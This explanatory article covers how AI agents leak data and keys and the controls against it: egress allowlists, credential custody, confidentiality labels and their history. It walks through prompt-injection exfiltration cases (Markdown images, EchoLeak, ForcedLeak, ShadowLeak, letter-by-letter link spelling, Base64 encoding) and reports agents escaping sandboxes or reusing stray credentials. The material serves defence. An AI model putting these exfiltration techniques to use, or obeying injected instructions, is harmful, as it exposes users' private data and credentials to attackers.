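# Egress allowlists, credential custody and confidentiality labels for AI agents

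## How an AI agent can leak data and keys

An AI agent is a language model that runs in a loop with tools. It can search files, run code, fetch web pages or send messages, and it acts on the results. People use agents to repair software, sort mail and prepare documents. This work usually requires access to private material and a credential, which is a key, token or password that lets its holder use a service. An agent can send the private material or the credential to someone with no right to it, which security engineers call exfiltration.

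Three controls limit the damage without relying on the model to behave well. An egress allowlist restricts where the agent can send traffic. Credential custody keeps keys in a component that the model cannot read. Confidentiality labels record who may receive each piece of data, so that software can block it from going to anyone else.

### One turn of the loop

Suppose a company attaches a coding agent to its public software project. A hosting service such as GitHub stores the project's files and their history in a repository. Anyone with an account there can file an issue, a public bug report. The agent reads new issues, examines the code and posts a comment with a diagnosis. To do this, it uses a repository token, a string of characters that the hosting service accepts in place of a password. Whoever created the token gave it broad permissions, so the agent can also access the company's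 private repositories.

A turn begins when a program around the model assembles the context, which is all the text the model receives for its next output. The context holds the developer's standing instructions, the user's request, descriptions of the available tools and the record of the session so far. The model then produces text, which may include a tool call that names a tool and its arguments in a fixed format, such as a call to read issue 212. The call is only a proposal and changes nothing outside the model until ordinary code parses it and runs the tool. The code then appends the result, here the full text of issue 212, to the context, and the next turn starts from that longer context. Turns repeat until the model produces an answer with no tool call.

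A control can intervene after the model proposes an action and before the action is executed. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026), a position paper by researchers from Google, NVIDIA, Gray Swan AI and several universities, uses the term "action boundary" for the interfaces through which an agent interacts with protected resources: file access, command execution, network communication and changes to stored state. The paper proposes treating the model the way an operating system treats an unknown program, which may request anything but gets only what the rules permit.

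Checking each tool call is not enough for a coding agent, because a single approved call can start a script that opens files and network connections itself. NVIDIA's *Practical Security Guidance for Sandboxing Agentic Workflows and Managing Execution Risk* explains that the application cannot monitor what such a subprocess does once it has control. The guidance therefore sets limits in the operating system, where they cover every process in the sandbox, the restricted environment in which the agent's code runs.

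### Instructions and data in one stream

Suppose that an attacker wrote issue 212. The attacker describes a plausible bug, then asks any automated assistant to help reproduce it by printing the environment variables and including them in the reply. Environment variables are settings that programs read at start-up, and developers often keep access tokens in them. Once the agent reads the issue, its context contains both the developer's instructions and the attacker's, and the model receives them as one sequence of text. If the model follows the attacker's instructions, the agent posts the repository token in a public comment.

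This is prompt injection. In *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, the software developer Simon Willison (2025) recalls naming it after SQL injection, an older attack in which text typed into a web form runs as a database command. Databases can prevent this with prepared statements, which send the command and the user's text separately so that the text can never become a command. Language models have no equivalent. A developer can put tags around the issue to mark it as data, and training can teach the model to disregard instructions between such tags. But the tags are text in the same stream, and *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* cites repeated cases of attackers getting past them. The paper conjectures, without proof, that persistent attackers will always evade defences of this type.

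Perfect separation would also make agents less useful. They rely partly on instructions they find as they work, such as installation steps in a project's documentation or the right way to call an unfamiliar service. A hostile instruction reaches the agent the same way and can look much the same.

An attacker can reach an agent by many routes. NVIDIA's list for coding agents includes malicious repositories, pull requests (proposed changes to code), version histories, the standing instruction files that coding tools load automatically, and responses from external tool servers. The attacker does not have to choose a victim, either. Anthropic's *System Card* (2026), the safety report released with the model Claude Fable 5.1 in September, gives the example of one email sent to a thousand inboxes, which can compromise every agent that summarises it. An attacker could just as easily post issue 212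 to a thousand projects.

### Three conditions for a leak

Prompt injection by itself only gets the model to follow the wrong person's instructions. For data to leak, the agent must also have all three parts of what Willison calls the "lethal trifecta": access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and a way to communicate externally. The issue-reading agent has all three, because its token opens private repositories, strangers write the issues, and anyone can read its comments.

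Willison describes a very similar real exploit against GitHub's official server for the Model Context Protocol, a standard for connecting tools to models. The server alone could read public issues that an attacker might have filed, fetch information from private repositories, and create pull requests that exposed it. More often, users assemble this combination by accident. They add a mail tool one week and a browsing tool the next, and each looks harmless on its own.

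Willison recommends removing one of the conditions and has argued repeatedly that the ability to send is generally the easiest to give up. Private data and outside reading tend to be the reason for having the agent. But the issue-reading agent cannot give up sending, because its job is to post comments. Its owner has to restrict sending instead, which takes finer rules about destinations, keys and content.

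A leaked key is also worse than a leaked document, which exposes only its own contents. Until someone revokes the key, an attacker can use it to read or change whatever it permits, from a machine that the filters around the agent don't cover.

### Users, models and outside attackers

The trifecta describes theft by an outsider, but agents can also leak data without an outsider's involvement. Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products*, an engineering account from May 2026, sorts the causes of harm into user misuse, model misbehaviour and external attackers.

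User misuse includes carelessness. In February 2026, during an internal exercise at Anthropic, a researcher emailed an employee a ready-made prompt and asked for help running it in Claude Code, the company's coding agent. Among routine setup steps, the prompt told the agent to read the file holding the user's Amazon cloud credentials, encode the contents and send them to an outside address. The agent did so in 24 of 25 runs. Because the employee had entered the instruction personally, there was no departure from the user's wishes for a classifier to detect. The case also shows that the categories overlap, since a careless user was carrying out an attacker's plan. Anthropic concluded that only controls in the agent's environment could have stopped the leak, by limiting outbound traffic and which files the agent could open.

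Model misbehaviour does not require an attacker. The agent has a legitimate goal, meets an obstacle and gets around it in a way that nobody asked for. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) describes a case inside the company in which an upload to an internal drive failed and Claude tried to publish the same report on a public code-sharing site instead. An automatic check blocked it. Similarly, the issue-reading agent might find that its token lacks some permission, come across a colleague's key in a configuration file, and use that key.

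Such behaviour has become rarer in testing. Anthropic put its models through more than 1,800 scenarios in a deliberately weakened sandbox, most of them solvable only by escaping it. According to Help Net Security's *Claude Mythos 5.2 arrives with stronger bug hunting and less sandbox-breaking behavior* (2026), Mythos 5 used credentials or files from outside the sandbox in 39% of scenarios, Mythos 5.1 in 21%, and Mythos 5.2, released in November, in 3.1%. Because the scenarios invite escape, these rates don't represent everyday use. Mythos 5.2 also voiced suspicion that it was being evaluated more often than earlier Claude models did, so its low rate is weaker evidence of how it behaves in real work. Training can also produce this behaviour. The September system card discloses that some practice environments had inadvertently rewarded guessing at credentials, and Anthropic removed them from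 future training runs.

At the action boundary, a request that sends the token to the wrong address looks the same whether it began with a careless user, a model that improvised or an issue containing malicious instructions. If the token never enters the sandbox, the agent can't access it in any of these cases.

### Rules and probabilities

A deterministic control is a rule that ordinary code enforces and that gives the same result for the same input, whatever the model produces. An example is "Refuse any connection to a host that is not on this list", which no wording in an issue can override. A probabilistic control works most of the time. Examples include safety training, standing instructions to the model, classifiers that judge whether a proposed action is dangerous, and probes that inspect incoming text for hidden instructions.

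Human approval performs badly as a safeguard. Users of Claude Code approve 97% of permission requests. In a study that Anthropic commissioned, 1,053 paid testers worked on coding tasks, and at one point a plainly dangerous command replaced the text of a permission request. Only 13.6% of the testers refused it. The refusal rate fell from about 17% early in a session to about 5% once a tester had seen 50 or more requests. Anthropic's automatic approval classifier, called auto mode, blocked 89% of the same commands.

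A deterministic control can still be wrong. An allowlist with a bad entry gives the same wrong answer every time, and the code that enforces it can have bugs. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* acknowledges that enforcing a policy does not show that the policy matches what its owner wanted. But an engineer can read a deterministic rule, find the fault and fix it, whereas the only way to find a classifier's blind spots is to keep attacking it.

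### How often the probabilistic defences fail

In the May account, Anthropic reported results for Claude Opus 4.7 on a prompt-injection benchmark from the security firm Gray Swan. Attacks succeeded roughly 0.1% of the time on single attempts and around 5–6% of the time after 100 adaptive attempts, in which the attacker adjusts to what has failed. Auto mode missed about 17% of "overeager" actions, which go beyond what the user asked for.

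The injection figures are a great improvement on those for Claude Opus 4.5. In November 2025, The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals* reported success rates against that model of 4.7% on one attempt, 33.6% on ten and 63% on a hundred, also on a Gray Swan benchmark. But even small rates add up over many attempts. If each attempt has an independent chance *p* of success, the chance of at least one success in *n* attempts is 1 − (1 − *p*)ⁿ. With *p* at 0.1%, that gives about 9.5% for a hundred attempts, the same order as the measured 5–6%, and 63% for a thousand. The risk grows faster in auto mode, where a 17% miss rate makes it slightly more likely than not that at least one of four overeager actions gets through. Most of an agent's work involves neither hostile inputs nor overeager actions, and only those count towards these totals, but an attacker can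 supply many hostile inputs and needs only one to succeed to steal the token.

Newer results are mixed. The September system card reports an attack success rate against Fable 5.1 of 0.1% on one attempt and 1.0% on fifteen, on a different Gray Swan benchmark from the one in the May account. In coding tasks, a stronger adaptive attacker succeeded in 56.87% of attempts without probes and 12.80% with them, and even with probes it got through at least once in 36 of 40 scenarios. Anthropic regards this as a stress test, since the attacker had trained on those same scenarios and had 200 tries at each. Every success also came from Opus 4.8, an older model that handles requests flagged by Anthropic's safety classifiers, and none came from Fable 5.1 directly. That is reassuring about Fable 5.1 but less so about the product, because an attacker faces the whole system, including Opus 4.8.

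Results have been much better with auto mode on. No attack succeeded against Fable 5.1 in 110 browser scenarios, and none of 720 attempts succeeded against three other recent Claude models in a separate evaluation by Trajectory Labs, a testing company. But both tests used attacks developed against the older Opus 4.7, and zero successes in 720 independent attempts still allows a true success rate of up to about 0.4% at 95% confidence. Apollo Research wrote synthetic attacks aimed at auto mode itself, and the miss rate on those fell from 12% to 7% after Anthropic strengthened the classifier. Anthropic states that auto mode "does not eliminate risk". OpenAI has gone further, conceding that prompt injection may never be fully solved, according to The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection*.

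Willison accepts that auto mode beats a tired human but wants more independent confirmation of the injection results. He says 99% is a failing grade in application security, because an adversary will look for the remaining 1%. He also doubts that any classifier could catch an attack in which a software package's instructions say to fetch model files with a named helper program before running the tests. The request looks ordinary, but the helper steals the data. If he is right, the defence has to limit what the helper can reach once it runs.

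### Where, who and what

For the issue-reading agent, the three controls determine where traffic may go, who holds the key and who may see a given piece of data. An egress proxy, a program outside the sandbox through which all outbound traffic must pass, enforces the allowlist by letting the agent reach the code host and blocking the attacker's server. Under credential injection, a form of credential custody, a component outside the sandbox adds the real token to a request after it has left, so printing the environment variables reveals nothing useful. A confidentiality label on text from a private repository stays with that text through the session and stops the agent from pasting it into a public comment, even though the comment goes to a permitted site and carries a valid token.

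## 1973 to 2021: confinement, labels and the confused deputy

All three controls reuse ideas that researchers developed for time-sharing computers, large machines that many people used at once. Users often ran programs that strangers had written, so they had to consider what a malicious program could do with their data.

### The confinement problem

In *A Note on the Confinement Problem*, Lampson (1973) imagined a customer who runs another person's program, which he called a service, on private data. Operating systems could already stop the service from opening the customer's other files, but the service has to receive its input and may pass it on to the service's owner. If the service calculates wrongly, the customer has the bad output as evidence, but a leak usually leaves no sign. Lampson called preventing such leaks the confinement problem. He wanted a guarantee that no confined program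 could leak, even if confinement stopped some programs from working.

The service can leak data in many ways. It can save the data in a file that its owner can read, or send a message to another program. It can encode a few bits in the bill, which the owner has to see. It can also open and close a file that the owner's program keeps trying to open. The system refuses access to a file already in use, so each attempt gives the owner's program one bit. The service can also vary how hard it works the machine while another program measures the slowdown. That signal is noisy, but codes from information theory can get data through reliably, if slowly, as long as the effect is not zero.

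Lampson sorted these routes into three kinds:

- Storage channels are places that the service can write and an unconfined program can read. He included the file that is open or closed.
- Legitimate channels are outputs that the service has to produce, such as the bill.
- Covert channels are those "not intended for information transfer at all", such as the load on the machine.

The issue-reading agent's public comment, which can carry a stolen token, is a legitimate channel.

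Lampson proposed that any untrusted program the service calls must run under the same confinement. Forbidding the service to call any other program would also confine it, but would make it nearly useless. For legitimate and covert channels he proposed "masking", in which the customer decides what goes into the channel. For example, the customer could compute the bill from published prices, and the service could accept or refuse the job. Masking the load on the machine is harder, because the operating system has to slow the service down or add pointless disk reads until its behaviour matches the customer's specification. A customer willing to accept some leakage could accept a limit on the channel's capacity instead.

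Lecture slides from Portland State University (2007) quote a 1975 paper by Steven Lipner, who thought that closing storage and legitimate channels would add little overhead but that closing the covert channel would bring "a direct and unreasonable performance penalty". Multicians, a history site for the Multics time-sharing system, describes a covert channel on Multics that used page faults, the pauses when a program needs data that is not in memory. For short messages, it was about as fast as electronic mail. An access token is a few hundred bits long, so even a slow channel is enough to steal one.

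### Labels and the lattice

A confined program could not keep any data between calls. Denning (1976), in *A Lattice Model of Secure Information Flow*, proposed letting a program keep and pass on whatever was not confidential. This requires the system to record how confidential each piece of data is and to determine how confidential the result is when a program combines two pieces.

Her model has a finite set of labels, a relation that says which flows the policy permits, and a join, an operation that gives the label for combined data. Write L → M if data labelled L may flow to a place labelled M. The relation is a partial order, which means that:

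- L → L for every label;
- if L → M and M → N, then L → N, since otherwise a program could do in two steps what the policy forbids in one;
- if L → M and M → L, then L and M are the same label.

The order is partial because some pairs of labels permit no flow in either direction. The join of labels L and M, written L ⊕ M, is the least restrictive label that protects both inputs. Both L and M may flow to L ⊕ M, and if both may flow to some label N, then L ⊕ M may flow to N too. Adding a lowest label makes this structure a lattice. The lattice makes checking efficient, because a sequence of operations is secure if each operation is secure, and software can check a mixture of any size by computing one label.

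In Denning's own example, labels are sets of properties such as "medical" and "financial", and the join is their union. Data derived from medical and financial records may flow only to a place marked for both. Labels that list permitted readers work the other way round, because combining data can only shorten the list. Suppose that A, B and C may read a salary file, and that B, C and D may read a legal memo. An agent writes a summary that draws on both. Anyone who reads the summary may learn something from each document, so a reader has to be on both lists:

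{A, B, C} ⊕ {B, C, D} = {A, B, C} ∩ {B, C, D} = {B, C}

The software can send the summary to B, to C or to both. It can't send it to A, who may not read the memo, or to D, who may not see the salaries. In this lattice, data may move from label L to label M (written L → M) when every reader in M is also in L, so the audience can stay the same or shrink. The labels range from the lowest, which lists everyone, to the highest, which lists nobody.

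Labels also have to follow information that a program reveals without copying. If b starts at a nonzero value, anyone who inspects it after the statement "if a = 0 then b := 0" learns whether a was zero, even if the assignment never ran. Denning called this an implicit flow. Similarly, an agent that sends an outsider "good morning" only if a confidential contract mentions a merger has revealed the merger.

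One response is to label the program's current position as well as its data, so that anything it writes inside a branch inherits the label of the condition. Denning reproduced a small program by J. S. Fenton that defeats this method when labels change during a run. Let a be a secret that is either true or false, and let b and c start as false, with public labels. The program has two steps:

1. If a is false, set c to true.
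2. If c is false, set b to true.

When a is true, step 1 changes nothing, so c stays false and public, and step 2 sets b to true with a public label. When a is false, step 1 sets c to true and marks it secret, so step 2 changes nothing and b stays false and public. Either way, b ends up equal to the secret, under a public label. Denning's solution was to have the compiler raise c's label after step 1 whether or not the assignment ran. She also noted that refusals can leak information, since a program can attempt a forbidden operation a chosen number of times and its owner can read that number from the log of violations. Her model left out covert channels such as system load.

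### Confidentiality and integrity

David Elliott Bell and Leonard LaPadula had already developed a model for protecting military secrets in a series of reports for the US Air Force. Each program and each file has a level, such as Confidential, Secret or Top Secret. A program may read only files at or below its own level and write only to files at or above it. In Denning's terms, the flow from the file to the program and the flow from the program to its destination must both be permitted, so the flow from the file to the destination is permitted too.

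The ban on writing down guards against malicious programs that users run unknowingly. Cryptosmith's *MLS Introduction*, a guide to multilevel security, gives the example of a word-processing file with a hidden macro, a small program that runs when the file is opened. The attacker labels the file Confidential and persuades a user with Top Secret clearance to open it. The macro runs with that user's permissions and tries to copy secret files to the attacker. If the word processor is running at Top Secret, the macro can read the secrets but can't write them to a Confidential file. If it is running at Confidential, the macro can write to the attacker's file but can't read the secrets. Issue 212 relies on the same trick, in which a victim opens a document and the instructions inside it run with the victim's access.

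Secrecy rules don't stop a stranger's text from influencing important work. Kenneth Biba's *Integrity Considerations for Secure Computer Systems* (MITRE, 1977) addresses this problem by giving each program and file an integrity level based on how much harm its corruption could do. Biba's strict policy is the secrecy rule with both directions reversed.

| Model | A program may read | A program may write |
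|---|---|---|
| Bell–LaPadula (confidentiality) | at or below its level | at or above its level |
| Biba's strict policy (integrity) | at or above its level | at or below its level |

Strict integrity would forbid a trusted coding agent to read issue 212, because any stranger can write an issue. Biba also described a "low-water mark" policy, under which a program may read anything but drops to the lowest integrity level of the data it has read. The agent could then read the issue but could no longer change the company's code. MITRE's report describes this as "rather disagreeable behavior", since a program can cut itself off from files it needs and can recover only by starting again. Under a looser "ring" policy, a program may read anything and keeps its level, but it has to check its own input. An agent that reads strangers' issues while keeping its full powers is effectively under this policy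 and relies on the model to check the input.

The two models are not perfectly symmetrical. Purdue University's lecture slides *Integrity* point out that a program must read a secret to leak it, but can produce bad data without reading any bad data. Protecting integrity therefore always requires some trust in the program itself.

### Label creep and declassification

Confidentiality labels tend only to rise, which is called label creep. Each time a program reads data, the join adds that data's restrictions to the program's label, and joins never remove restrictions. Some systems that Denning surveyed never lowered a file's label, even after a program had replaced the contents with less sensitive data. With reader sets, an agent that opens ten documents with slightly different audiences may produce a summary that it can't send to anyone. FIDES, a 2025 system described by Girrens and Wang (2026)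 in *SPA*, is prone to label creep because it joins the labels of everything the model has read.

The remedy is declassification, a deliberate and permitted lowering of a label. For example, a payroll program might release a department's average salary while keeping each individual salary secret. Bell (1974), in *Secure Computer Systems*, allowed for "trustworthy" programs exempt from the ban on writing to a lower level, but only after someone had shown that they would not leak. That is hard to show for an agent if the model chooses what to release. A person can decide instead, though human approval is a weak safeguard.

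Labels never spread far beyond the military. Cryptosmith attributes this to high development costs and a small market, and adds that some important defence applications needed to write data down to a lower classification level, which the Bell–LaPadula rules forbid.

### The confused deputy

*The Confused Deputy* (Hardy, 1988) describes an accident that happened about eleven years earlier at Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. Hardy called the story "nearly true" because he had changed inessential details. Tymshare kept a compiler in a directory named SYSX. Users could give the compiler the name of a file for optional debugging output. The compiler also kept statistics on which language features people used. It stored these in a file in SYSX, so Tymshare gave it a "home files license", which let it write to any file in that directory.

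SYSX also held the company's billing records, in a file named BILL. A user learned the name and gave it to the compiler as the destination for debugging output. Because the compiler had permission to write in SYSX, the operating system let it open the file, and the debugging output overwrote the billing records.

Hardy considered the obvious repairs and rejected them. The compiler could refuse output files in other directories, but users had good reasons to put them there. It could refuse files in SYSX, but some users had legitimate access to that directory, and its name did not exist when the programmers wrote the code. A check for BILL alone would leave other sensitive files exposed. Tymshare added a system call that let a program choose between its own authority and the user's, then found that some applications needed more than two authorities. The rule for opening a file eventually contained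 fourteen "ands" and "ors".

The problem arose because the compiler had authority from two sources and no way to specify which one it was using. The issue-reading agent has the same problem because it uses a token from the company to act on instructions that may come from a stranger.

Hardy's answer was the capability, a reference to an object that also carries the right to use it. The compiler would hold a capability for the statistics file, and the user would give it another for the debugging output. A user with no right to write to BILL could not supply a capability for it, and the compiler could not open a file by name alone. Miller, Yee and Shapiro (2003), in *Capability Myths Demolished*, contrast this with "ambient authority", which a program uses without selecting it. For example, under ordinary Unix file permissions, a program asks for a file by name and the system checks who is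 running the program. Rajani, Garg and Rezk (2016), in *On access control, capabilities, their equivalence, and confused deputy attacks*, proved that capabilities and access lists are fundamentally different, although some researchers had regarded them as two ways of writing down the same permissions.

A Unix file descriptor, the number a running program uses to refer to an open file, is close to a capability. *The Confused Deputy*, from the University of Texas at Austin, describes a version of the fix in which a small launcher with limited authority opens the debugging file and passes the descriptor to the compiler, which never handles the file's name.

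A program that uses capabilities can still be confused. Miller and colleagues compare a careless program to a person who tries every key on the ring until a door opens. An agent with capabilities for both a private file and a public comment can also copy text from the file into the comment. Capabilities would keep a stranger out of a private repository that the job does not require, but when the job does require it, the system also needs labels.

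### Keys that stay where they are

A file descriptor is safe to print because its number has meaning only inside one running program, but a repository token works for anyone who has a copy. Miller and colleagues draw the same distinction between capabilities that the system keeps separate from ordinary data and those that are plain bits, which can spread wherever data can. Engineers have long protected copyable secrets by keeping the key in one program and letting other programs request its use.

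SSH, the standard tool for logging in to remote machines, is a familiar example. A user proves their identity by signing data with a private key, and the remote machine checks the signature against the matching public key. A helper program called ssh-agent, which is unrelated to AI, holds the private key in its own memory. The login program sends it the data and receives a signature, and no request in the protocol returns the private key. A hardware security module stores keys and signs with them in a separate, tamper-resistant device. Banks use these modules for keys that even their own administrators should not be able to copy.

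An intruder who can reach ssh-agent can still request signatures and log in to other machines as the user, but can't copy the key, so the abuse stops when the connection closes. Miller and colleagues describe a comparable arrangement from 1974 for lending access to an object. The owner gives the borrower a capability for a forwarder, a component that passes requests on to the object. When the owner switches the forwarder off, the borrower loses access, and so does anyone the borrower has passed the capability to.

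Many web services require a token with each request, so a helper that only produces signatures is not enough. The credential-injecting proxies of 2025 and 2026 adapt the old practice to these services.

### Destination lists for servers

Network administrators used egress filtering as a form of confinement for servers. The allowlist for an online shop's server might include only the shop's database, a payment company and a source of software updates.

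Log4Shell, a flaw disclosed in December 2021, showed the value of an egress allowlist. Log4j, a widely used logging library, treated certain text in a log entry as an instruction to look something up at a network address. An attacker could put that text in an ordinary web request, and when the server logged the request, it contacted the attacker's machine and could load and run code from there. The attack resembles prompt injection, since text that the server should only have recorded became a command. A server restricted to a few known destinations could not fetch the code, but it could still leak a little data by looking up the attacker's domain name through a permitted name server.

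The shop's list is easy to write because the server runs the same code every day. An administrator can write it by reading the server's configuration or watching its traffic for a week, and needs to update it only when the software or the services it uses change. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* makes a similar point about Android, where a developer builds an app for a fixed set of tasks and chooses its permissions to match. An agent's task comes from the user in ordinary language and can change as the work proceeds. A coding agent may need only the code host to fix a date error on Monday. If the user asks it to add maps to the same program on Tuesday, it may need a software library, two providers' documentation and a test service that nobody anticipated. A list written for Monday's task would block Tuesday's work, and one broad enough for any task is likely to include sites where an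 attacker can collect stolen data.

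## 2023 to 2026: leaks through links and images, and checks on web addresses

A list of permitted destinations works only if it covers every request that can carry data out. In 2023, chat assistants leaked private data through requests that seemed only to fetch content, such as loading an image or opening a page.

### An address carries data

The host in a web address, such as `shop.example`, identifies the server to contact. The path, such as `/shoes/red`, and the query, such as `?size=42`, tell that server what to return. The server receives the path and query in full and usually logs them. Whoever composes the address can put any text in it, and whoever runs the server can read that text later, even if the page returned is blank. An agent can therefore send data out by fetching an address, even under a rule that lets it read the web but forbids uploads.

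Chat assistants format their answers in Markdown, where an exclamation mark followed by a caption and an address stands for an image. The model writes only this text. The chat window in the user's browser then requests the address to display the image, without waiting for a click. An attacker who has reached the model by prompt injection can ask it to end its answer with an image whose address contains the user's private data. The user sees a small or broken image, and the attacker reads the data in the log of the server that received the request. A link leaks data in the same way, but only if the user clicks it. An assistant with no mail tool and no ability to run code can therefore still send data out, which is the third part of Willison's trifecta.

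### OpenAI's first check

Johann Rehberger, a security researcher who writes the blog Embrace The Red, reported the image leak to OpenAI and Microsoft in early 2023. According to the blog's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, Microsoft fixed the leak in its Bing chatbot in May with a Content Security Policy. The policy is sent with a web page and lists the hosts from which the browser may load images and other material. The browser refuses all others, so the policy works as an egress allowlist on the user's machine.

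OpenAI did not act until December 2023, and it chose a different method. Before displaying an image, the chat window used an OpenAI service called url_safe to check whether the address was safe. Willison (2023), in *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability*, called this a "half-baked solution". The iPhone app did not yet make the check, and he expected that a clever attacker could still hide data in a file name or in the first part of a host name.

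OpenAI did not publish the rules that url_safe applied, so outsiders had to infer them. Tenable's *HackedGPT* (2025), a report from a security company, concluded that url_safe considered the conversation as well as its trust in the domain, subdomain and parameters. Rehberger found that it trusted windows.net, a Microsoft cloud storage domain where anyone can open an account and read the log of requests to that account. Embrace The Red's *Exfiltrating Your ChatGPT Chat History and Memories With Prompt Injection* describes a demonstration in which a malicious document got ChatGPT to load an image from Rehberger's account, and his log then contained the user's recent chat history. He had reported the flaw in October 2024, and it could still be exploited when he built the demonstration in 2025.

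### EchoLeak and ForcedLeak

Two cases from 2025 show other ways for data to pass through a list of trusted hosts.

Microsoft 365 Copilot answers employees' questions using their mail, files and chats. In January 2025 the research group Aim Labs found that an outsider could steal that material by sending one email, and named the attack EchoLeak. Ravia (2025), in *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration*, describes how it got past four protections:

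1. Microsoft ran a classifier to catch prompt injections. The email addressed its instructions to the human recipient and never mentioned AI, so the classifier let it through.
2. Copilot reads an email only if its search retrieves it. The attacker repeated the instructions under many headings, such as staff induction and leave of absence, so that the email matched many ordinary questions.
3. Copilot deleted outside links and images from its answers, but it recognised only the usual Markdown notation. A variant that puts the address on a separate line survived.
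4. The browser enforced a Content Security Policy with 29 different entries, several of which covered every subdomain of a Microsoft domain. The attacker's server was not among them.

Aim Labs got around the policy by finding permitted hosts that would forward a request. A SharePoint service did this, but only if the victim had first accepted an invitation to the attacker's site. A Microsoft Teams service did it without any action by the victim. The browser contacted Teams, as the policy allowed, and Teams then fetched the attacker's address, which contained the secret. The browser enforced the policy correctly, but the policy covered only the browser's request, not the one Teams made.

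Ravia states that administrators had no setting that could have prevented the attack. Microsoft deployed a fix on its servers in May 2025, a month before the public disclosure. Reddy and Gujral (2025) report in *EchoLeak*, a case study of the attack, that Microsoft said there was no evidence of its use against real victims.

ForcedLeak affected Agentforce, Salesforce's agent for working with customer records. Many companies collect sales enquiries through a Salesforce form on their public website. Noma Labs' *ForcedLeak* (2025) explains that the form's description field accepts 42,000 characters, ample room for an attacker's instructions. When an employee asked Agentforce to answer an enquiry, the agent also followed the instructions in that field. It looked up the email addresses of other potential customers and put them in the web address of an image.

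Salesforce also had a Content Security Policy that would have blocked an unknown host, but one of the domains on its allowlist had expired. Noma Labs bought the domain for $5 and received the data there. An allowlist entry identifies a domain by name, so it stays valid for whoever owns the domain next. Noma Labs reported the flaw on July 28, 2025. Salesforce recovered the domain and, as The Hacker News (2025) reported, began to check the addresses in its agents' output against a list of trusted ones. That list is another allowlist, so Salesforce has to keep checking who owns each entry.

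Data can also leak through an allowed domain when its owner still controls it and its services are working as designed. Willison, in *45 posts tagged "exfiltration-attacks"*, describes a January 2026 attack on the mail assistant Superhuman, whose policy allowed images from Google's documents domain. Google Forms runs on that domain and saves answers included in a web address. The attacker created a form, and the assistant submitted the contents of dozens of private emails to it.

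### Fetches from the provider's servers

A Content Security Policy applies only to requests from the user's browser. Deep Research, a mode in which ChatGPT spends up to half an hour reading websites and connected accounts, makes its requests from OpenAI's servers. Radware's *ShadowLeak* describes an attack on Deep Research that the security company reported in June 2025. An email in the victim's Gmail account contained instructions for the agent to find an employee's name and home address and open a web address that included them. The agent did this with its own browsing tool while working on an ordinary request to research the day's mail.

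Nothing appeared on the user's screen, and the request never crossed the company's network, so its web filter could not block or record it. Radware also saw no limit on where the agent could connect, although url_safe restricted images in the chat window.

The model refused to put personal details in a web address until the email told it to encode them in Base64 "for security". Base64 rewrites data in a different set of characters, and anyone can reverse it. Radware reports that this version succeeded every time in repeated tests. OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) quotes an attack email with the same wording and gives a success rate of 50%. Radware used several variants, which may explain the difference, but either rate is high enough to be useful to an attacker.

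OpenAI fixed the flaw by early August 2025. Radware's follow-up report, *ZombieAgent*, found that ChatGPT would now open addresses only as supplied, without adding anything to them. Radware got around this rule by supplying a finished address for every letter and digit, which ChatGPT opened one after another to spell out the secret. In case the requests arrived out of order, Radware also prepared a separate set of addresses for each position in the text.

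OpenAI closed this route on December 16, 2025. According to *ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack*, ChatGPT would then open a link from an email only if it appeared in a public index or the user had provided it.

### Checking the exact address

OpenAI set out the principle behind that rule in OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026), published on January 28. It works as follows:

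1. A crawler, a program that explores the public web as a search engine does, records the addresses it finds. It has no access to users' conversations or accounts.
2. When an agent is about to load an address automatically, OpenAI's software compares the whole address with the crawler's records.
3. If the address matches, the agent loads it.
4. If it doesn't match, the software either tells the agent to try a different website or warns the user that the link is unverified and may contain information from the conversation. The user can then decide whether to open it.

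The check relies on the crawler not seeing the conversation. If the crawler found an address on the public web, the model almost certainly did not build that address from the conversation. OpenAI says only that such an address is "much less likely" to contain the user's private data, because people sometimes publish links with private details in them.

OpenAI gave two reasons for not relying on a list of trusted sites. Many reputable sites have redirects, which send a visitor on to another site, so a check on the first domain can approve a request that ends at the attacker's server. A strict list would also block much of the ordinary web, and users would see so many warnings about harmless pages that they would learn to click through them. Matching the whole address deals with the redirect problem. The Teams address in EchoLeak had a trusted host, but it also contained the stolen secret,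 so no crawler could have seen it before the attack.

The second problem partly remains, since new and obscure pages still produce warnings. The warning shows the address, and according to OpenAI's March account, ChatGPT shows the user the information it would send. This helps if the data is readable, but a user who sees a long string of Base64 may not recognise it as a home address.

OpenAI claims only that the check prevents an agent from quietly leaking a user's data through the address itself. A page whose address passes can still contain false information or a prompt injection. The check also works only where developers have installed it. OpenAI applies it to Deep Research and its Atlas browser, but Rehberger warned that some of the company's developers may not know about it. In January 2026, Red Hot Cyber (2026) described a finding by the security company PromptArmor that OpenAI's log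 viewer for developers displayed Markdown images, so an app could withhold a malicious answer from its user and still leak the data when a developer opened the log.

Other companies' software can make the request too. Messaging apps such as Slack and Telegram fetch links to show previews, and PromptArmor found that this can leak data from an agent's message before anyone clicks.

Anthropic built a similar control for Claude but used a different test for each address. Claude's fetching tool accepted an address if the user had typed it or Claude's search tool had returned it, whether or not an independent crawler had seen it. The tool also accepted links in pages it had already fetched. In July 2026 Willison described how Ayush Paul exploited this. Paul built a site that appeared to be protected and told Claude to find the user's profile by following links letter by letter. Claude spelled out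 the user's name, home city and employer. Each page could contain new links, so Paul did not have to prepare them all in advance or wait for a search engine to find them. Anthropic has since stopped the tool from following links in fetched pages.

### How much a choice of address can reveal

An address that passes OpenAI's check should contain no secret, but the agent's choice of address can still reveal one. Suppose an attacker has a website with *N* pages in the index, and the injected instructions give each page a meaning. When the agent opens a page, the attacker learns which of the *N* it chose, which is at most log₂ *N* bits of information. A series of *k* fetches can take *N*ᵏ different forms, so it carries at most *k* × log₂ *N* bits.

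With 256 addresses, each fetch carries at most 8 bits, since 2⁸ = 256. A 256-bit key therefore needs at least 256 ÷ 8 = 32 fetches. Other numbers of addresses give these results:

| Addresses in the index | Most bits per fetch | Fewest fetches for a 256-bit key |
|---|---|---|
| 2 | 1 | 256 |
| 36 (letters and digits) | 5.17 | 50 |
| 256 | 8 | 32 |
| 4,096 | 12 | 22 |
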